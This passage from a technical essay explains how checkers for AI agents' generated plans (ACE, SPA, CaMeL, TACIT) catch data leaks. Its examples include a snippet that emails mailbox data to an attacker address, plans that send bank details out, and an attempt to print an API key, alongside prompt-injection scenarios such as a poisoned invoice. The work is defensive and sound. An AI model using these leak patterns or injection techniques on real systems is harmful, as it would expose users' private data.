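Choosing a tool from a dictionary is easier to check, because the plan lists the candidates, here `save_file` and `send_email`, and a checker can consider both. It would reject the plan because of `send_email` even if `choice` were always `"save"`. But Python also lets a later line add an entry to the dictionary, or make the name `save_file` refer to `send_email`, so the checker can rely on the list only if the language forbids such changes.

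Aliasing, where two names refer to the same object, can make a careless checker accept a leak:

```
report = []
notes = report
notes.append(fetch_mail())
send_email(to="backup@attacker.example", body=str(report))
```

`report` and `notes` are two names for the same list. A checker that follows data name by name would record mailbox data in `notes` but none in `report`, so it would let the email through. A better checker tracks which names may share an object, but it can only approximate this, and in a large program it may treat many unrelated objects as possibly the same. A language can avoid the problem by forbidding changes to existing values, since two names for one list are harmless if nothing can alter the list.

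### Four kinds of plan language

Designers have chosen languages that differ widely in how much they allow:

| Plan language | What a plan can contain | What a checker can work out |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed workflow in JSON | A sequence of calls that pass results on by name | Every call, its order and the source of its data |
| Python subset, as in ACE | Branches, loops and arithmetic as well | All calls and data flows that might occur, including some that never will |
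| Graph of states and guarded transitions | Branches and repetition among a fixed set of stages | Every route through the graph, and so which calls can follow which |
| Full typed language without its unsafe features | Functions, data structures and most ordinary code | Whatever the type rules cover, such as the effects a function may have |

Soteria, which checks plans against tool contracts, uses state graphs. A guard in a state graph is a condition that must hold before the plan moves to the next stage. The Scala programming language's safe mode is an example of the last approach.

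Suppose a shopkeeper asks an agent to check the stock of item A12 and to email the buyer if fewer than ten are left. In the style of ACE's Python subset, the plan is:

```
def main():
    stock: int = StockLevel(item="A12")
    if stock < 10:
        EmailSender(to="buyer@shop.example", body="A12 is low")
    return stock
```

In Meijer's JSON format, without the descriptions that he gives each step, it might be:

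```
{ "name": "check_stock",
  "steps": {
    "look_up": {
      "function": { "name": "stock_level",
                    "arguments": { "item": "A12" } },
      "result": "stock",
      "next": "notify" },
    "notify": {
      "function": { "name": "email_if_below",
                    "arguments": { "value": "stock", "limit": 10,
                                   "to": "buyer@shop.example" } },
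      "result": "sent",
      "next": "finish" },
    "finish": { "return": "stock" } } }
```

Each step in this format has one successor, so the checker only has to follow the `next` fields and confirm that no step repeats. Software can also generate the user's explanation from the same structure, as Meijer proposes, so that it always matches the program.

But a format with one successor per step cannot express the condition, so the JSON version moves the comparison with ten into a tool called `email_if_below`. The checker can establish who may get an email, but it has to rely on a description of that tool to establish when the email is sent. A simple plan language can thus push logic into tools that somebody has to trust. A designer could add a conditional step, but the format would then be a more verbose version of the Python subset.

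The JSON examples are also ambiguous, because Meijer uses a quoted string both for a constant, such as the file pattern `*.txt`, and for the name of an earlier result, such as `emails_fetched`. The checker and the executor must resolve this ambiguity identically. Otherwise the executor runs a different program from the one the checker approved.

### ACE's restrictions

Li and colleagues require every ACE plan to have a single entry point, `main()`. Plans may contain if-statements, but for-loops may run only over a range of integers, whose length a variable can set. A while-loop's condition must be a single variable, and neither kind of loop may contain `break`. The planner's prompt also requires every variable to have a declared type, and forbids function calls inside larger expressions and modifying values in place.

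Besides its invented tools, a plan can call a small part of Python's standard library and a few built-in functions. One built-in asks the user for input, another displays a result, and a third, `GetAllImplementations`, returns every installed tool that fits an invented one. The plan can then choose which of those tools to call, but it can't look up arbitrary functions by name.

Li and colleagues say that the loop restrictions simplify the later analysis. To follow the language's rules, the planner mostly has to write a few extra lines. For example, the expression `"The answer is: " + str(result)` breaks the rule on nested calls, so the planner first stores `str(result)` in a variable and then joins the two strings. This gives every intermediate result a name that the checker can attach a label to. Requiring the loop condition to be a single variable has the same effect. If plans could use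 `break`, a condition could determine whether statements several lines later in the loop body run, and the checker would have to trace that influence to statements outside the `if`.

Rice's theorem still applies to ACE under these rules. A plan can recompute the variable that controls a while-loop arbitrarily, so a planner could still write the Goldbach loop. ACE's checker therefore has to approximate, and the restrictions make the approximation simpler to compute. In a stricter language without while-loops, every plan would finish if its tools did, because Python fixes the length of an integer range before a for-loop starts.

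The planner is a language model and may ignore a rule in its prompt, so the checker has to parse the plan and reject any construct that is not on a list of permitted ones. A list of forbidden words is much weaker. Searching for `exec`, for instance, misses a plan that uses reflection to look up a function by the name `"ex" + "ec"`.

### Do models do better or worse in code?

A checkable language is of little use if models write poor plans in it. Meijer had no measurements of plan quality in 2025, but two studies from 2026 provide some.

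Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026), in *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, gave 14 models 309 tasks from BFCL v4, a benchmark of function calling. Each model did the tasks once with JSON tool calls and once by writing Python scripts. Eleven models did at least as well with scripts. GPT-5.6 Sol and Terra improved most, with Sol rising from 72.2% to 82.8%. Three models, GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini, did 20 to 27 points worse with scripts. They wrote a backslash and the letter n where a line break belonged, so any script longer than one line failed with a syntax error.

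Patel and colleagues conclude that success with code depends on a model's generation, and they call the three failing models older. The release dates do not fit this conclusion well. GPT-5.4-mini, one of the three, came out in March 2026, seven months after GPT-5 and GPT-5-nano, which did not make the mistake. The newest models' gains also look smaller beside GPT-4o's 81.9% with JSON calls, since scripts brought GPT-5.6 Sol to about that level.

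Scripts had a clearer advantage when a task needed very many calls. Claude Sonnet 5 began to drop JSON calls when a task required 70 to 72 of them at once, but with a script it made all 100 calls in the largest test. On 52 tasks with chains of dependent calls, its accuracy rose from 80.8% to 96.2%. This gain is weaker evidence about planning than it seems, because the tools were stubs that returned only their own arguments. In a script, the model had to work out each intermediate value itself, whereas a real plan would leave a variable for the tool's result.

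Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026), in *Is Bash All You Need?*, used longer office tasks. They compared direct tool calls with restricted Python programs, which could act only through the same catalogue of tools, and with bash, a command-line shell that can run almost anything. Their average scores were:

| Benchmark and model | Direct calls | Restricted programs | Shell |
|---|---|---|---|
| TheAgentCompany, Claude Opus 4.8 | 44.9% | 52.9% | 69.4% |
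| TheAgentCompany, GPT-5.5 | 45.3% | 45.1% | 67.1% |
| APEX-Agents, Claude Opus 4.8 | 41.1% | 40.1% | 48.5% |
| APEX-Agents, GPT-5.5 | 39.8% | 37.8% | 44.6% |

Restricted programs did about as well as direct calls, with a gain in one case out of four, and used 15% to 57% fewer tokens. They also failed more often. On TheAgentCompany, 65% of program runs reported success, against 93% of direct calls. Mak and colleagues suggest this is because a program must also coordinate several calls and handle failures along the way.

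The shell beat restricted programs by 7 to 22 points, but shell plans are harder to check because a shell command can start other programs and build new commands from strings. Part of the gap probably came from the actions available rather than the language, since the shell let agents do things that the tool catalogue did not. For TheAgentCompany, the researchers had written the 60-tool catalogue themselves. A better catalogue might narrow the gap without making plans harder to check. Mak and colleagues recommend the shell where it can run in isolation, and restricted programs where security or compliance rules require a fixed set of tools.

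Neither study tested a planner that writes one complete plan in advance. Patel and colleagues scored only the calls, and the agents on TheAgentCompany typically ran about nine restricted programs per task and could read results between programs. ACE's planner does write its complete plan in advance, but Li and colleagues did not compare it with the same models making direct calls. What an agent loses by planning in advance, which Meijer asked about, remains unmeasured.

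### Generated code in products

Companies have adopted generated code mainly to save tokens. *Code Mode* (Varda and Pai, September 2025) describes how Cloudflare turns an agent's tools into a TypeScript interface and gives the model a single tool that runs code. Varda and Pai argue that models have seen code from millions of real projects but only contrived examples of tool calls. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* (Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to tools) followed in November. In its example, an agent copies a meeting transcript from Google Drive into a sales database. Direct tool calls would pass the whole transcript through the model twice, whereas code sends it straight from one tool to the other. The agent also loads only the tool definitions it needs, which cuts the total from 150,000 tokens to 2,000.

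Cloudflare later put its entire interface of more than 2,500 operations behind two functions, `search()` and `execute()`. Carey reports in *Code Mode* that describing these two functions takes about 1,000 tokens, whereas describing a separate tool for each operation would take 1.17 million. He calls the generated code "a compact plan".

None of the three posts describes a static check of that code before it runs, nor does OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling*, which documents a similar feature. Safety depends on a sandbox (a confined environment for running code) and on controls over the tools. Cloudflare's sandbox has no general internet access, and software outside it holds the access keys, so the generated code cannot leak them. Users choose which permissions to grant when they connect an agent to Cloudflare's interface. OpenAI runs each program in a fresh JavaScript environment and advises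 developers to check the arguments and permissions of every call in their own application. Anthropic recommends resource limits and monitoring, and mentions that the software between the agent and its tools could enforce fixed rules about where data may go.

A sandbox confines a program to its permitted tools but does not restrict what the program does with them. If Michelle's assistant is allowed to fetch and send mail, a program that forwards her mailbox to an attacker stays inside the sandbox. The planner isn't isolated either, because it usually reads one program's output before writing the next.

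Some of these interfaces would also be hard to check. In Varda and Pai's example, the generated TypeScript gives tool results the type `any`, which turns off type checking for them. Carey's `execute()` gives the program one general function, `cloudflare.request()`, and the operation depends on the method and web path passed to it as strings. A checker would have to determine those strings before it could distinguish a harmless lookup from a deletion. OpenAI lets programs call a shell as a tool, and the command they pass to it is code in a string.

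OpenAI advises developers to use direct calls for writes and for actions that need approval, to "preserve a clear authorization boundary". Meijer would instead put such actions in the checked plan. OpenAI's advice makes sense for programs that nobody has checked, since a separate call gives the user or the application a chance to refuse.

A developer could add the missing check to OpenAI's feature. When a program needs a function that runs in the developer's application, OpenAI pauses the program and sends the application the pending call and the program's full source code. The application could then analyse the source and refuse to run any of its functions. Tools that run on OpenAI's side may already have acted by then, so the check would be sure to come before any tool runs only if the program calls no tools except the application's functions.

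## Checking where data can flow before the plan runs

A checker can use a plan's source code to work out which data might reach which tool. For Michelle's assistant, this meant noticing that mailbox data went into a summary and the summary went into an outgoing email. Information-flow analysis replaces this informal reasoning with rules that software can apply to any plan. The rules give each piece of data a label and update the labels line by line. For now, a label records only how secret the data is.

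### Labels and lattices

Suppose a user's sensitive data falls into three categories: financial, medical and personal. A label is a set of these categories. A bank statement has the label {financial}, a hospital bill might have {financial, medical}, and public data has the empty label {}. Each tool also has a label, called its clearance, which lists the categories the tool may receive.

Data may flow into a tool if the tool's clearance includes every category in the data's label. The symbol for "may flow into" is ⊑, so {financial} ⊑ {financial, personal}. Some labels, such as {financial} and {medical}, are not comparable because neither may flow into the other.

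If a plan copies a bank statement and a blood test into one document, the document needs a label that covers both. This is the join of the two labels, written ⊔:

```
{financial} ⊔ {medical} = {financial, medical}
```

The label {financial, medical, personal} would also cover both, but the join is the lowest label that does, so it restricts the document no more than necessary. The meet, written ⊓, is the highest label that two labels both cover. If a document has to go to one tool with clearance {financial, personal} and another with clearance {medical, personal}, it may contain only personal data, because that is the only category in both clearances.

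Three categories give eight labels, and data may flow upwards from any label to one that contains it:

```
              {financial, medical, personal}

{financial, medical}  {financial, personal}  {medical, personal}

     {financial}            {medical}            {personal}

                               {}
```

Mathematicians call such an order a lattice if every two elements have a join and a meet. In 1976 the computer scientist Dorothy Denning proposed lattices as a general model of secure information flow. With a lattice, a checker needs only one label per variable, however many sources contributed to its value. *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, a 1977 paper, describes a check based on this model that is simple enough for most compilers to include. The check can prove that a program's supposedly public results do not depend on its confidential inputs, even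 in ways that don't involve copying a secret into a result.

### ACE's rules

Li and colleagues use Denning's model to check ACE's plans after the concrete planner has proposed installed tools for them. The user labels each request by how sensitive it is, and all variables start with that label. ACE also adds the request's label to every flow in the plan, because the planner read the request before writing the plan. A request labeled {medical} therefore can't use any tool that lacks medical clearance, even a weather tool. The requests in the examples below are public.

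ACE first translates the plan into a list of flows. In an internal flow, the plan's own code combines data, for instance by joining two strings. Nothing leaves the interpreter, so any combination is allowed, and ACE only has to update the labels. In an external flow, data passes through a tool, which might leak it, so ACE also checks the tool's clearance. For inputs `x1` to `xn` and an output variable `y`, the rules are:

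```
internal flow:
    new label(y) = label(y) ⊔ label(x1) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(xn)

external flow through tool f:
    required:      label(x1) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(xn) ⊑ clearance(f)
    new label(y) = clearance(f)
```

Some destinations, such as a storage location on the user's computer, have fixed labels. ACE does not change them, and it checks that the data is allowed to flow to those destinations.

The last line of the external rule is deliberately pessimistic. It gives a tool's output the tool's whole clearance, whatever the inputs, because the tool may return something it already had access to. For example, a tool that takes no arguments can still return a secret access key.

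Two further rules cover whole programs. A sequence `S1; S2` is secure if `S1` is secure and `S2` is secure when it starts with the labels resulting from `S1`. For a loop, ACE analyses the body repeatedly until the labels stop changing, then checks the body with those final labels.

### Three leaking plans

The simplest of Li and colleagues' examples loads bank details and emails them:

```
data = load_bank_details()
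send_email(content=data)
```

The loading tool has clearance {financial} and the email tool has clearance {personal}.

| Line | Label going in | Tool's clearance | Check | Label of `data` afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `load_bank_details()` | {} | {financial} | Passes | {financial} |
| `send_email(data)` | {financial} | {personal} | Fails | |

ACE rejects this choice of tools before loading anything. It then tries other installed tools that fit the plan, and gives up only if no combination passes.

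In the next example, the leak does not happen the first time through the loop:

```
a = ""
for i in range(4):
    network_send(a)
    a = load_bank_details()
```

The first call to `network_send` sends an empty string. The second sends the bank details, which the plan loaded at the end of the first round. A checker that read the loop body once from top to bottom would see the call before the secret existed and accept the plan. ACE's repeated analysis finds the leak. Suppose that `network_send` has the empty clearance:

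| Pass | `a` at the start | Check on `network_send(a)` | `a` at the end |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | {} | Passes | {financial} |
| 2 | {financial} | Fails | {financial} |

The labels are the same at the end of pass 2 as at the start, so further passes would find nothing new, however many times the loop runs. Some leaks take more passes to detect. If the loop body sent `a`, then copied `b` into `a` and `c` into `b`, and only then loaded the bank details into `c`, the plan would first leak them in its fourth round, and the analysis would need four passes to detect this. Li and colleagues point out that drawing an arrow from each input to each output and searching the drawing for a path gives the same answer.

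The third example reveals part of a secret without copying it:

```
a = SecretInfo()
b = ""
if a[0] == "0":
    b += "0"
else:
    b += "1"
network_send(b)
```

Li and colleagues' version ends with the `if` statement; the last line here adds the call that would leak the result. No line assigns `a` to `b`, but anyone who receives `b` learns whether the secret starts with a zero. A loop that asked enough such questions about each character could copy the whole secret. To catch this, ACE treats the condition as a hidden variable and adds it to the inputs of every statement in both branches. If `SecretInfo` has clearance {financial}, the labels are:

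| Flow | Label going in | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `SecretInfo()` into `a` | {} | `a` becomes {financial} |
| `a` into the condition | {financial} | The condition becomes {financial} |
| Condition into `b`, in either branch | {financial} | `b` becomes {financial} |
| `b` into `network_send`, clearance {} | {financial} | Check fails |

The rule also covers tool calls inside a branch. The shopkeeper's plan in the previous section emails the buyer "A12 is low" if fewer than ten are left. The text is a constant, but the buyer learns something about the stock from the email's arrival. ACE would accept that plan only if the email tool had clearance for stock data.

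ACE's printed rules seem to have a gap where two branches meet again. Suppose `wants_balance` is public and `get_weather` has the empty clearance:

```
if wants_balance:
    text = load_bank_details()
else:
    text = get_weather()
send_email(content=text)
```

The translation that Li and colleagues print puts the statements of one branch after those of the other. The first branch gives `text` the label {financial}, and the second replaces it with {}, because an external flow overwrites the old label. The email then passes the check, even though the plan sends the bank details whenever `wants_balance` is true. The same rules reject the plan if the branches are swapped. The standard remedy is to analyse each branch separately and join the resulting labels, which would give {financial} in either order. ACE's software may already do this, but the published rules do not include it.

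ACE's loop rule is also limited because it assumes that every loop ends. A plan could loop forever if the user's balance is zero and otherwise send the word "done". ACE treats the statements inside a loop as depending on the loop's condition, but not the statements after it, so it would miss that the absence of the message reveals a zero balance.

### A safe plan that ACE rejects

Suppose the user wants the agent to summarize a public web page and email the summary to a friend:

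```
page = fetch_page(url="https://news.example")
summary = summarize(text=page)
send_email(content=summary)
```

The user also has the agent summarize bank letters and test results, so the summarizer has clearance for all three categories.

| Line | Label going in | Tool's clearance | Check | Label of the result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `fetch_page` | {} | {} | Passes | {} |
| `summarize` | {} | {financial, medical, personal} | Passes | {financial, medical, personal} |
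| `send_email` | {financial, medical, personal} | {personal} | Fails | |

This is a false alarm if the summarizer works only from the text it receives. If it keeps a copy of yesterday's bank letter and includes it in today's summary, the rejection is correct. The rule cannot distinguish the two cases, so it rejects the plan in both. This puts general-purpose tools at a disadvantage, because they need broad clearances to be useful. The user could install another summarizer with clearance only for public data, and ACE would then find a combination that passes.

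The rule for internal flows causes false alarms too, because it never lowers a label. If a plan loads bank details into `note` and later replaces them with the words "See you at ten", `note` keeps the label {financial}, so the plan can't email the harmless text unless the planner puts it in a new variable. Li and colleagues do not report how often ACE's flow analysis rejects useful plans.

### Adding labels for trust

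Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, describe a similar checker that gives each tool separate labels for what it may receive and what it may add to its output. The output's label is the join of the inputs' labels and the label for what the tool adds. If a summarizer adds nothing secret, a summary of a public page stays public, and the plan above passes. This relies on whoever configures the system being right that the summarizer doesn't retain content from earlier documents.

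SPA's plans are JSON programs with branches and loops, but the checker reads each plan only once. It can do this because a plan may not assign a variable twice, and a variable created inside a branch or loop does not exist outside it. A variable therefore cannot carry a secret from one round of a loop to the next, so the checker does not need repeated passes over the loop. Two branches also cannot leave different labels on the same variable, so the checker does not need to merge labels after a branch.

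The checker also tracks how trustworthy data is. When a plan combines data, the result is as secret as the most secret input and, as in f-Secure, only as trustworthy as the least trusted one. Before each tool call, the checker requires:

```
secrecy(inputs) ⊑ the most secret data the tool may receive
the least trust the tool accepts ⊑ trust(inputs)
```

Suppose a user asks the agent on Monday to fetch an invoice and on Tuesday to pay it, but an attacker has put their own account number in the invoice. The planner never reads the invoice and plans to pay it, as the user asked. Secrecy labels don't help, because the account number isn't secret. SPA rejects Tuesday's plan if the payment tool accepts only trusted inputs. SPA stores Monday's result with its label and shows Tuesday's planner only a description of the result, so the invoice is still untrusted when the new plan retrieves it.

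Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano, a small model, on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks and, in their tests, 949 attack runs:

| SPA's configuration | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Complete plan in advance, no label check | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Complete plan in advance, with label check | 29.0% | 0.0% |

The label check stopped four attacks that succeeded without it, all on the same banking task, but nearly halved the number of tasks completed. It rejected the plan in about 53% of trials, typically because the plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that required trusted input. The security gain was small partly because most of the benchmark's attacks, like InjecAgent's, put instructions into tool outputs that the planner never reads. The invoice attack depends on a false value instead, and the results are little evidence of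 how often such attacks would succeed without labels.

Most of the rejected plans probably did break the rule by letting untrusted data influence a protected tool, even where the user would have been happy with the outcome. A more precise analysis would therefore accept few more of them. The rule itself is too strict for tasks such as paying a bill that arrives by email. Girrens and Wang suggest setting requirements for individual arguments, so that an email tool could require a trusted address but accept untrusted text in the body. They also suggest raising a value's trust level after an explicit check.

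### Source-to-sink rules

Meijer's rule for Michelle's mailbox needs no lattice. It names a source, a sink and a condition, roughly as follows:

```
source:     the result of fetch_email
sink:       the body of a send_email call
condition:  the recipient is not in *.valleysharks.com
```

The checker looks for a path from the source to the sink through the plan's assignments and calls. CodeQL and Semgrep run the same kind of query. The checker finds such a path in the plan that the poisoned tool description produced, so it rejects that plan.

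Such a rule is easy to write. Meijer's rule distinguishes colleagues from outsiders, which ACE cannot do because it gives `send_email` one clearance for all recipients. Labels can also make this distinction if they list people instead of categories. In *APPA* (2026), each label includes the set of permitted readers, and when two pieces of data are combined, only readers permitted for both may receive the result.

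A source-to-sink rule protects only the routes it lists. If a rule covers only the body of an email, a plan could still send Michelle's mail to the attacker in the subject line or in a calendar invitation. With labels, the mailbox data would keep its label on every route, and the checker would compare that label with the clearance of whichever tool received the data.

A query that follows only assignments and calls would also miss the example with `a[0]`, since no assignment leads from `a` to `b`. Meijer's JSON format has no branches, but a tool can branch internally. The `email_if_below` tool from the previous section takes the stock level as a number to compare, not as a message body, so a rule about message bodies would not apply.

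The names in the rule must also match those in the workflow. Meijer's printed rule names `fetch_email`, while his workflow calls `fetch_mail`. A checker that compared these names literally would find no source in the workflow and accept the leak. In the usual pattern notation, `*.valleysharks.com` also fails to match an address such as `michelle@valleysharks.com`, so the rule would treat colleagues as outsiders. These are mistakes in an illustration, but a real rule with the same mistakes would protect nothing, and its users would get no warning.

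### Labels during the run

An agent can instead label data as it runs and check each tool call against the labels on its actual arguments. This is more precise because it considers only the path the agent has taken. For example, a sound static checker has to reject the plan that emails either the bank details or the weather, because the plan might send the bank details. A run-time tracker blocks the email only if it contains the bank details.

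Run-time labels also describe a tool's output more precisely. f-Secure's monitor, for example, labels each message in a search result separately. A static checker runs before the search, when the messages' senders are unknown, so it has to treat the whole result as untrusted.

But a tracker that looks only at the path taken can miss what the other path would have revealed:

```
b = "no"
if overdrawn:
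    b = "yes"
network_send(b)
```

Suppose `overdrawn` has the label {financial}. If it is true, the tracker adds that label to `b` and blocks the call. If it is false, the assignment inside the `if` never runs, `b` keeps its public label, and the call sends "no". The receiver then knows that the user is not overdrawn. A static checker examines the assignment whether or not it will run, so it gives `b` the label {financial} and rejects the plan. To catch this leak, a run-time tracker would have to inspect the skipped branch, which is itself a form of static analysis.

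CaMeL is the best-known system that tracks labels while the plan runs. Li and colleagues say it uses a custom Python interpreter to enforce fine-grained restrictions on data and control flow. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) add that CaMeL's plans cannot define their own functions. They also argue that a value loses its labels once it enters a model's conversation as text.

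Tracking data through a language model is hard because nobody can say which parts of a prompt influenced the answer. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) distinguishes explicit influence, where fragments of the input reappear in the output, from implicit influence, where the input affects the output without reappearing in it. It gives each label a confidence score between 0 and 1. These scores can help detect attacks, but a checker that ignored labels with low scores would not be sound.

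The cautious alternative is to give a model's output the join of the labels of everything the model has read. Girrens and Wang describe the run-time system FIDES as keeping such a label for the planner's whole context and checking every tool call against it. This preserves the labels, but *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) warns that the context's label can quickly become too restrictive. After the planner reads one untrusted page, every later call counts as untrusted. Both FIDES and CaMeL therefore use Willison's arrangement to keep untrusted data out of the planner's context. SPA applies the cautious rule to each quarantined model call separately, so a summary gets the labels of its source documents and the rest of the plan is unaffected.

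### Missing and wrong labels

All of these checks depend on somebody having assigned the right labels. If nobody has marked `load_bank_details` as financial and it has the empty clearance, the analysis of the first example changes as follows:

| Line | Label going in | Tool's clearance | Check | Label of `data` afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `load_bank_details()` | {} | {} | Passes | {} |
| `send_email(data)` | {} | {personal} | Passes | |

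ACE would accept the plan and email the bank details if they lacked a proper label. Li and colleagues say that users have to label every information source, including their own requests, and that the analysis will not detect leaks from a source without a proper label. Overly generous clearance also allows leaks. If `send_email` had financial clearance, ACE would accept the original plan even if the bank details were labeled correctly. The labels are therefore part of the trusted base, along with the checker and the interpreter.

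*APPA* uses partial labels for data whose sources are not all labelled. Each partial label records what the system already knows about a piece of data and lists its unlabelled sources. Treating data from every unlabelled source as maximally secret and untrusted would be safe, but an agent with many unlabelled tools could then do very little. *APPA* guarantees that any check that passes with partial labels would also pass if those sources had complete labels, so missing labels do not make the check more permissive. The guarantee does not protect against incorrect labels.

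## Using a type system to limit what generated code can do

Besides tracking labels on the data in a plan, a checker can track what each piece of code is able to do. A function that cannot send anything cannot leak a bank statement, whatever it computes from the statement. TACIT, which Odersky and colleagues built at the Swiss university EPFL and published in 2026, applies this idea to agents. The agent writes its plans in Scala 3, a full programming language, and only plans that pass the compiler's type checker may run.

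### Capabilities and capture checking

A capability is a value, such as a handle for writing to a particular file, that code must hold to perform an effect. In ordinary Python, any line can open any file by naming it. In a capability-safe language, code cannot make a handle for itself, so it can write to a file only if other code has given it the handle. The idea dates from work on operating systems in the 1960s.

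Functions make capabilities hard to keep track of, because a function can carry one inside it:

```
val out   = File("report.txt")
val save  = (s: String) => out.write(s)
val shout = (s: String) => s.toUpperCase
```

Both functions take a string. But `save` also keeps a reference to `out`, so anyone who calls it can write to the file without having the handle. In most languages, the type of `save` gives no hint of this. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds the missing information:

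```
save:   String ->{out} Unit
shout:  String -> String
```

The braces list the capabilities that a function can reach, and `Unit` means that it returns no useful value. A single arrow without braces marks a pure function, which holds no capabilities, so it can compute a result but cannot write a file, send a message or change anything outside itself. A double arrow, `=>`, allows a function any capabilities.

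The type system still tracks a capability when another object wraps it. If a logger stores `out`, its type becomes `Logger^{out}`, and any function that uses the logger has the logger in its own list. The compiler accepts a function that uses fewer capabilities than the program allows, but rejects one that uses more. It infers most of these lists, so the agent rarely has to write them.

The compiler checks each function against the declared types of whatever it uses, without tracing data through the whole program. This is useful in a full language, where functions can take other functions as arguments. Odersky and colleagues point out that tracing precisely where each function ends up can take time that grows exponentially with the program's size.

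### A planner that may be working for the attacker

TACIT is a server that existing agents, such as Claude Code, can connect to as they would to any other tool. The agent sends it a snippet of Scala. TACIT compiles the snippet with capture checking and runs it only if the compiler accepts it. Otherwise, TACIT returns the compiler's error to the model, which can try again. A snippet can access files, run commands and use the network only through TACIT's library.

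Each snippet is a short plan, and the model reads its output before writing the next one, so TACIT does not require the agent to plan the whole task in advance. TACIT also does not stop hostile text in an ordinary file or web page from reaching the model.

Odersky and colleagues allow for this by not trusting the planner at all. They assume that a cloud provider hosts the model and that the model may be cooperating fully with an attacker. They also distrust the agent's software, every snippet it submits and everything it reads from outside. They trust the Scala compiler, TACIT's library, the software that runs the compiled code and, optionally, a second language model that runs locally. TACIT's guarantee about secrets is meant to hold even if an attacker writes the plan, whereas f-Secure's guarantee fails if the planner reads one hostile page.

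The type system can protect files only if the agent has no other way to reach them. lampepfl's *TACIT*, the documentation for the EPFL group's code, recommends turning off the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools. An agent that keeps its shell can print a secret file with one command that the compiler never checks.

### A wrapper for secrets

The user marks some folders as classified. When a snippet reads a file from one of them, the library returns the text in a wrapper called `Classified`. Its most important method is:

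```
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`T` is the type of the contents, such as `String`. The method `map` applies a function to the contents and wraps the result. The plain arrow in `op: T -> U` means that `map` accepts only pure functions. The agent has no method for extracting the contents, and printing a wrapped value gives only `Classified(****)`.

The compiler accepts this snippet, which summarizes a confidential contract:

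```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val doc = readClassified("/project/secrets/contract.txt")
  val summary = chat(doc.map(text => s"Summarize this: $text"))
  writeClassified("/project/secrets/summary.txt", summary)
}
```

The function inside `map` is pure because it only puts words in front of the text. `chat` passes the wrapped prompt to the trusted local model and wraps the answer. The model that wrote the snippet never receives the contract or the summary. This is Willison's pair of models again, except that the model without tools is the trusted one.

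In the team's tests, the compiler rejected an agent's attempt to print an API key from inside `map`. Shortened and with other names, the snippet was:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val apiKey = readClassified("/project/secrets/github.txt")
  apiKey.map(k => println(k))
}
```

According to the error message, `map` requires a function of type `String -> Unit`, but the snippet supplied one of type `String ->{x$1} Unit`.

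In TACIT, `println` requires an output capability, which the compiler supplies automatically and here names `x$1`. The function that prints the key therefore has `x$1` in its capability list, but `map` accepts only functions whose list is empty, so the compiler rejected the snippet. Running it would have leaked the key, because anything the snippet prints goes back to the cloud model. The compiler also rejected an attempt to write classified text to a file from inside `map`, because that function's list contained the file's handle.

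The wrapper also stops a plan from leaking a secret by testing whether it starts with a zero and sending a different message in each case. Only code inside `map` can read the secret and branch on it, and the result of that code stays wrapped. ACE needs a special rule for conditions to catch this leak.

The same restriction blocks some useful plans. Suppose a user wants the agent to email a colleague if a classified contract expires this month. A snippet can check the expiry date and show the user the answer, but it cannot use that answer to decide whether to send the email.

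Users still need to see the results, so TACIT has two output channels. If a snippet prints the wrapped summary, the user's terminal shows the text and the cloud model receives `Classified(****)`. The summary remains available in the next turn of the conversation. If the user asks how long it is, the model can write `summary.map(_.length)` and print the result. Again, only the user sees the number.

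### File permissions that end with their block

A snippet gets access to files by calling `requestFileSystem` with a folder and a block of code. The library creates a file-system capability, passes it to the block and cancels it when the block ends. A snippet might try to keep the access for later:

```
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("notes.txt").read()
}
bad()
```

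The block returns a function that would read the file only when called, by which time the permission should have ended. The function holds `fs`, so `fs` must appear in its type. But the type of the block's result must be valid outside the block, where `fs` does not exist, so the compiler rejects the snippet. In the tests, agents made this mistake by returning a list of file handles from the block.

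Because `requestFileSystem` requires the output capability, a snippet can't open a folder from inside `map` either. The library checks each path when the snippet tries to open a file, and refuses any path outside the requested folder. The compiler does not check paths, which may depend on data that arrives during the run.

The time limit only partly restrains the agent, because an agent whose permission has ended can ask for a new one in its next snippet, and its own code names the folder. Whoever configures the server therefore has to limit which folders the agent can request. According to Glama's *TACIT*, a later copy of the project's documentation, the administrator can list the folders that agents may request. Without a list, the server allows only the folder in which it started.

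### Safe mode

Full Scala has features that would let a program lose track of its capabilities. A type cast, for example, makes the compiler treat a value as having a different type. An agent could cast the printing function to `String -> Unit` and pass it to `map`. Safe mode is a restricted form of the language that closes these gaps. Scala's *Safe Mode*, the official reference page, lists six restrictions:

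1. Programs may not use unchecked type casts or pattern matches.
2. They may not use the library module of unsafe capability operations.
3. They may not use annotations that switch off checks.
4. They may not use reflection at run time.
5. The compiler must run capture checking and track every change to stored data.
6. Programs may use global objects only if those objects are themselves safely implemented.

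The first four stop a program from dropping a capability from a type. The fifth makes the lists complete, and the sixth keeps out library functions whose effects the types do not record.

Useful libraries often break these rules internally. For example, a function that caches its earlier results changes stored data, although its callers cannot tell. A programmer can exempt such code from the restrictions by marking it `@assumeSafe`, but must then establish by other means that it is safe. In the reference page's example, a mail module asks the user to confirm each message and then calls an unchecked mailer. The compiler would accept the module even without the confirmation step. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala*, an introduction by a Scala consultancy, notes that a safe-mode program cannot use the annotation, because an agent could then exempt its own code.

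Safe mode does not control exceptions, which a program throws when something goes wrong. A function inside `map` could be written to throw one only when a key begins with "a", and a caller who saw the failure would learn the key's first letter. Tracking every possible division by zero in the types would be impractical, so TACIT catches exceptions during the run and turns them into ordinary values, which can stay wrapped. In some of the team's tests, TACIT hid exceptions inside `map`, so a bug there left the user with a blank answer and the model with no error to correct.

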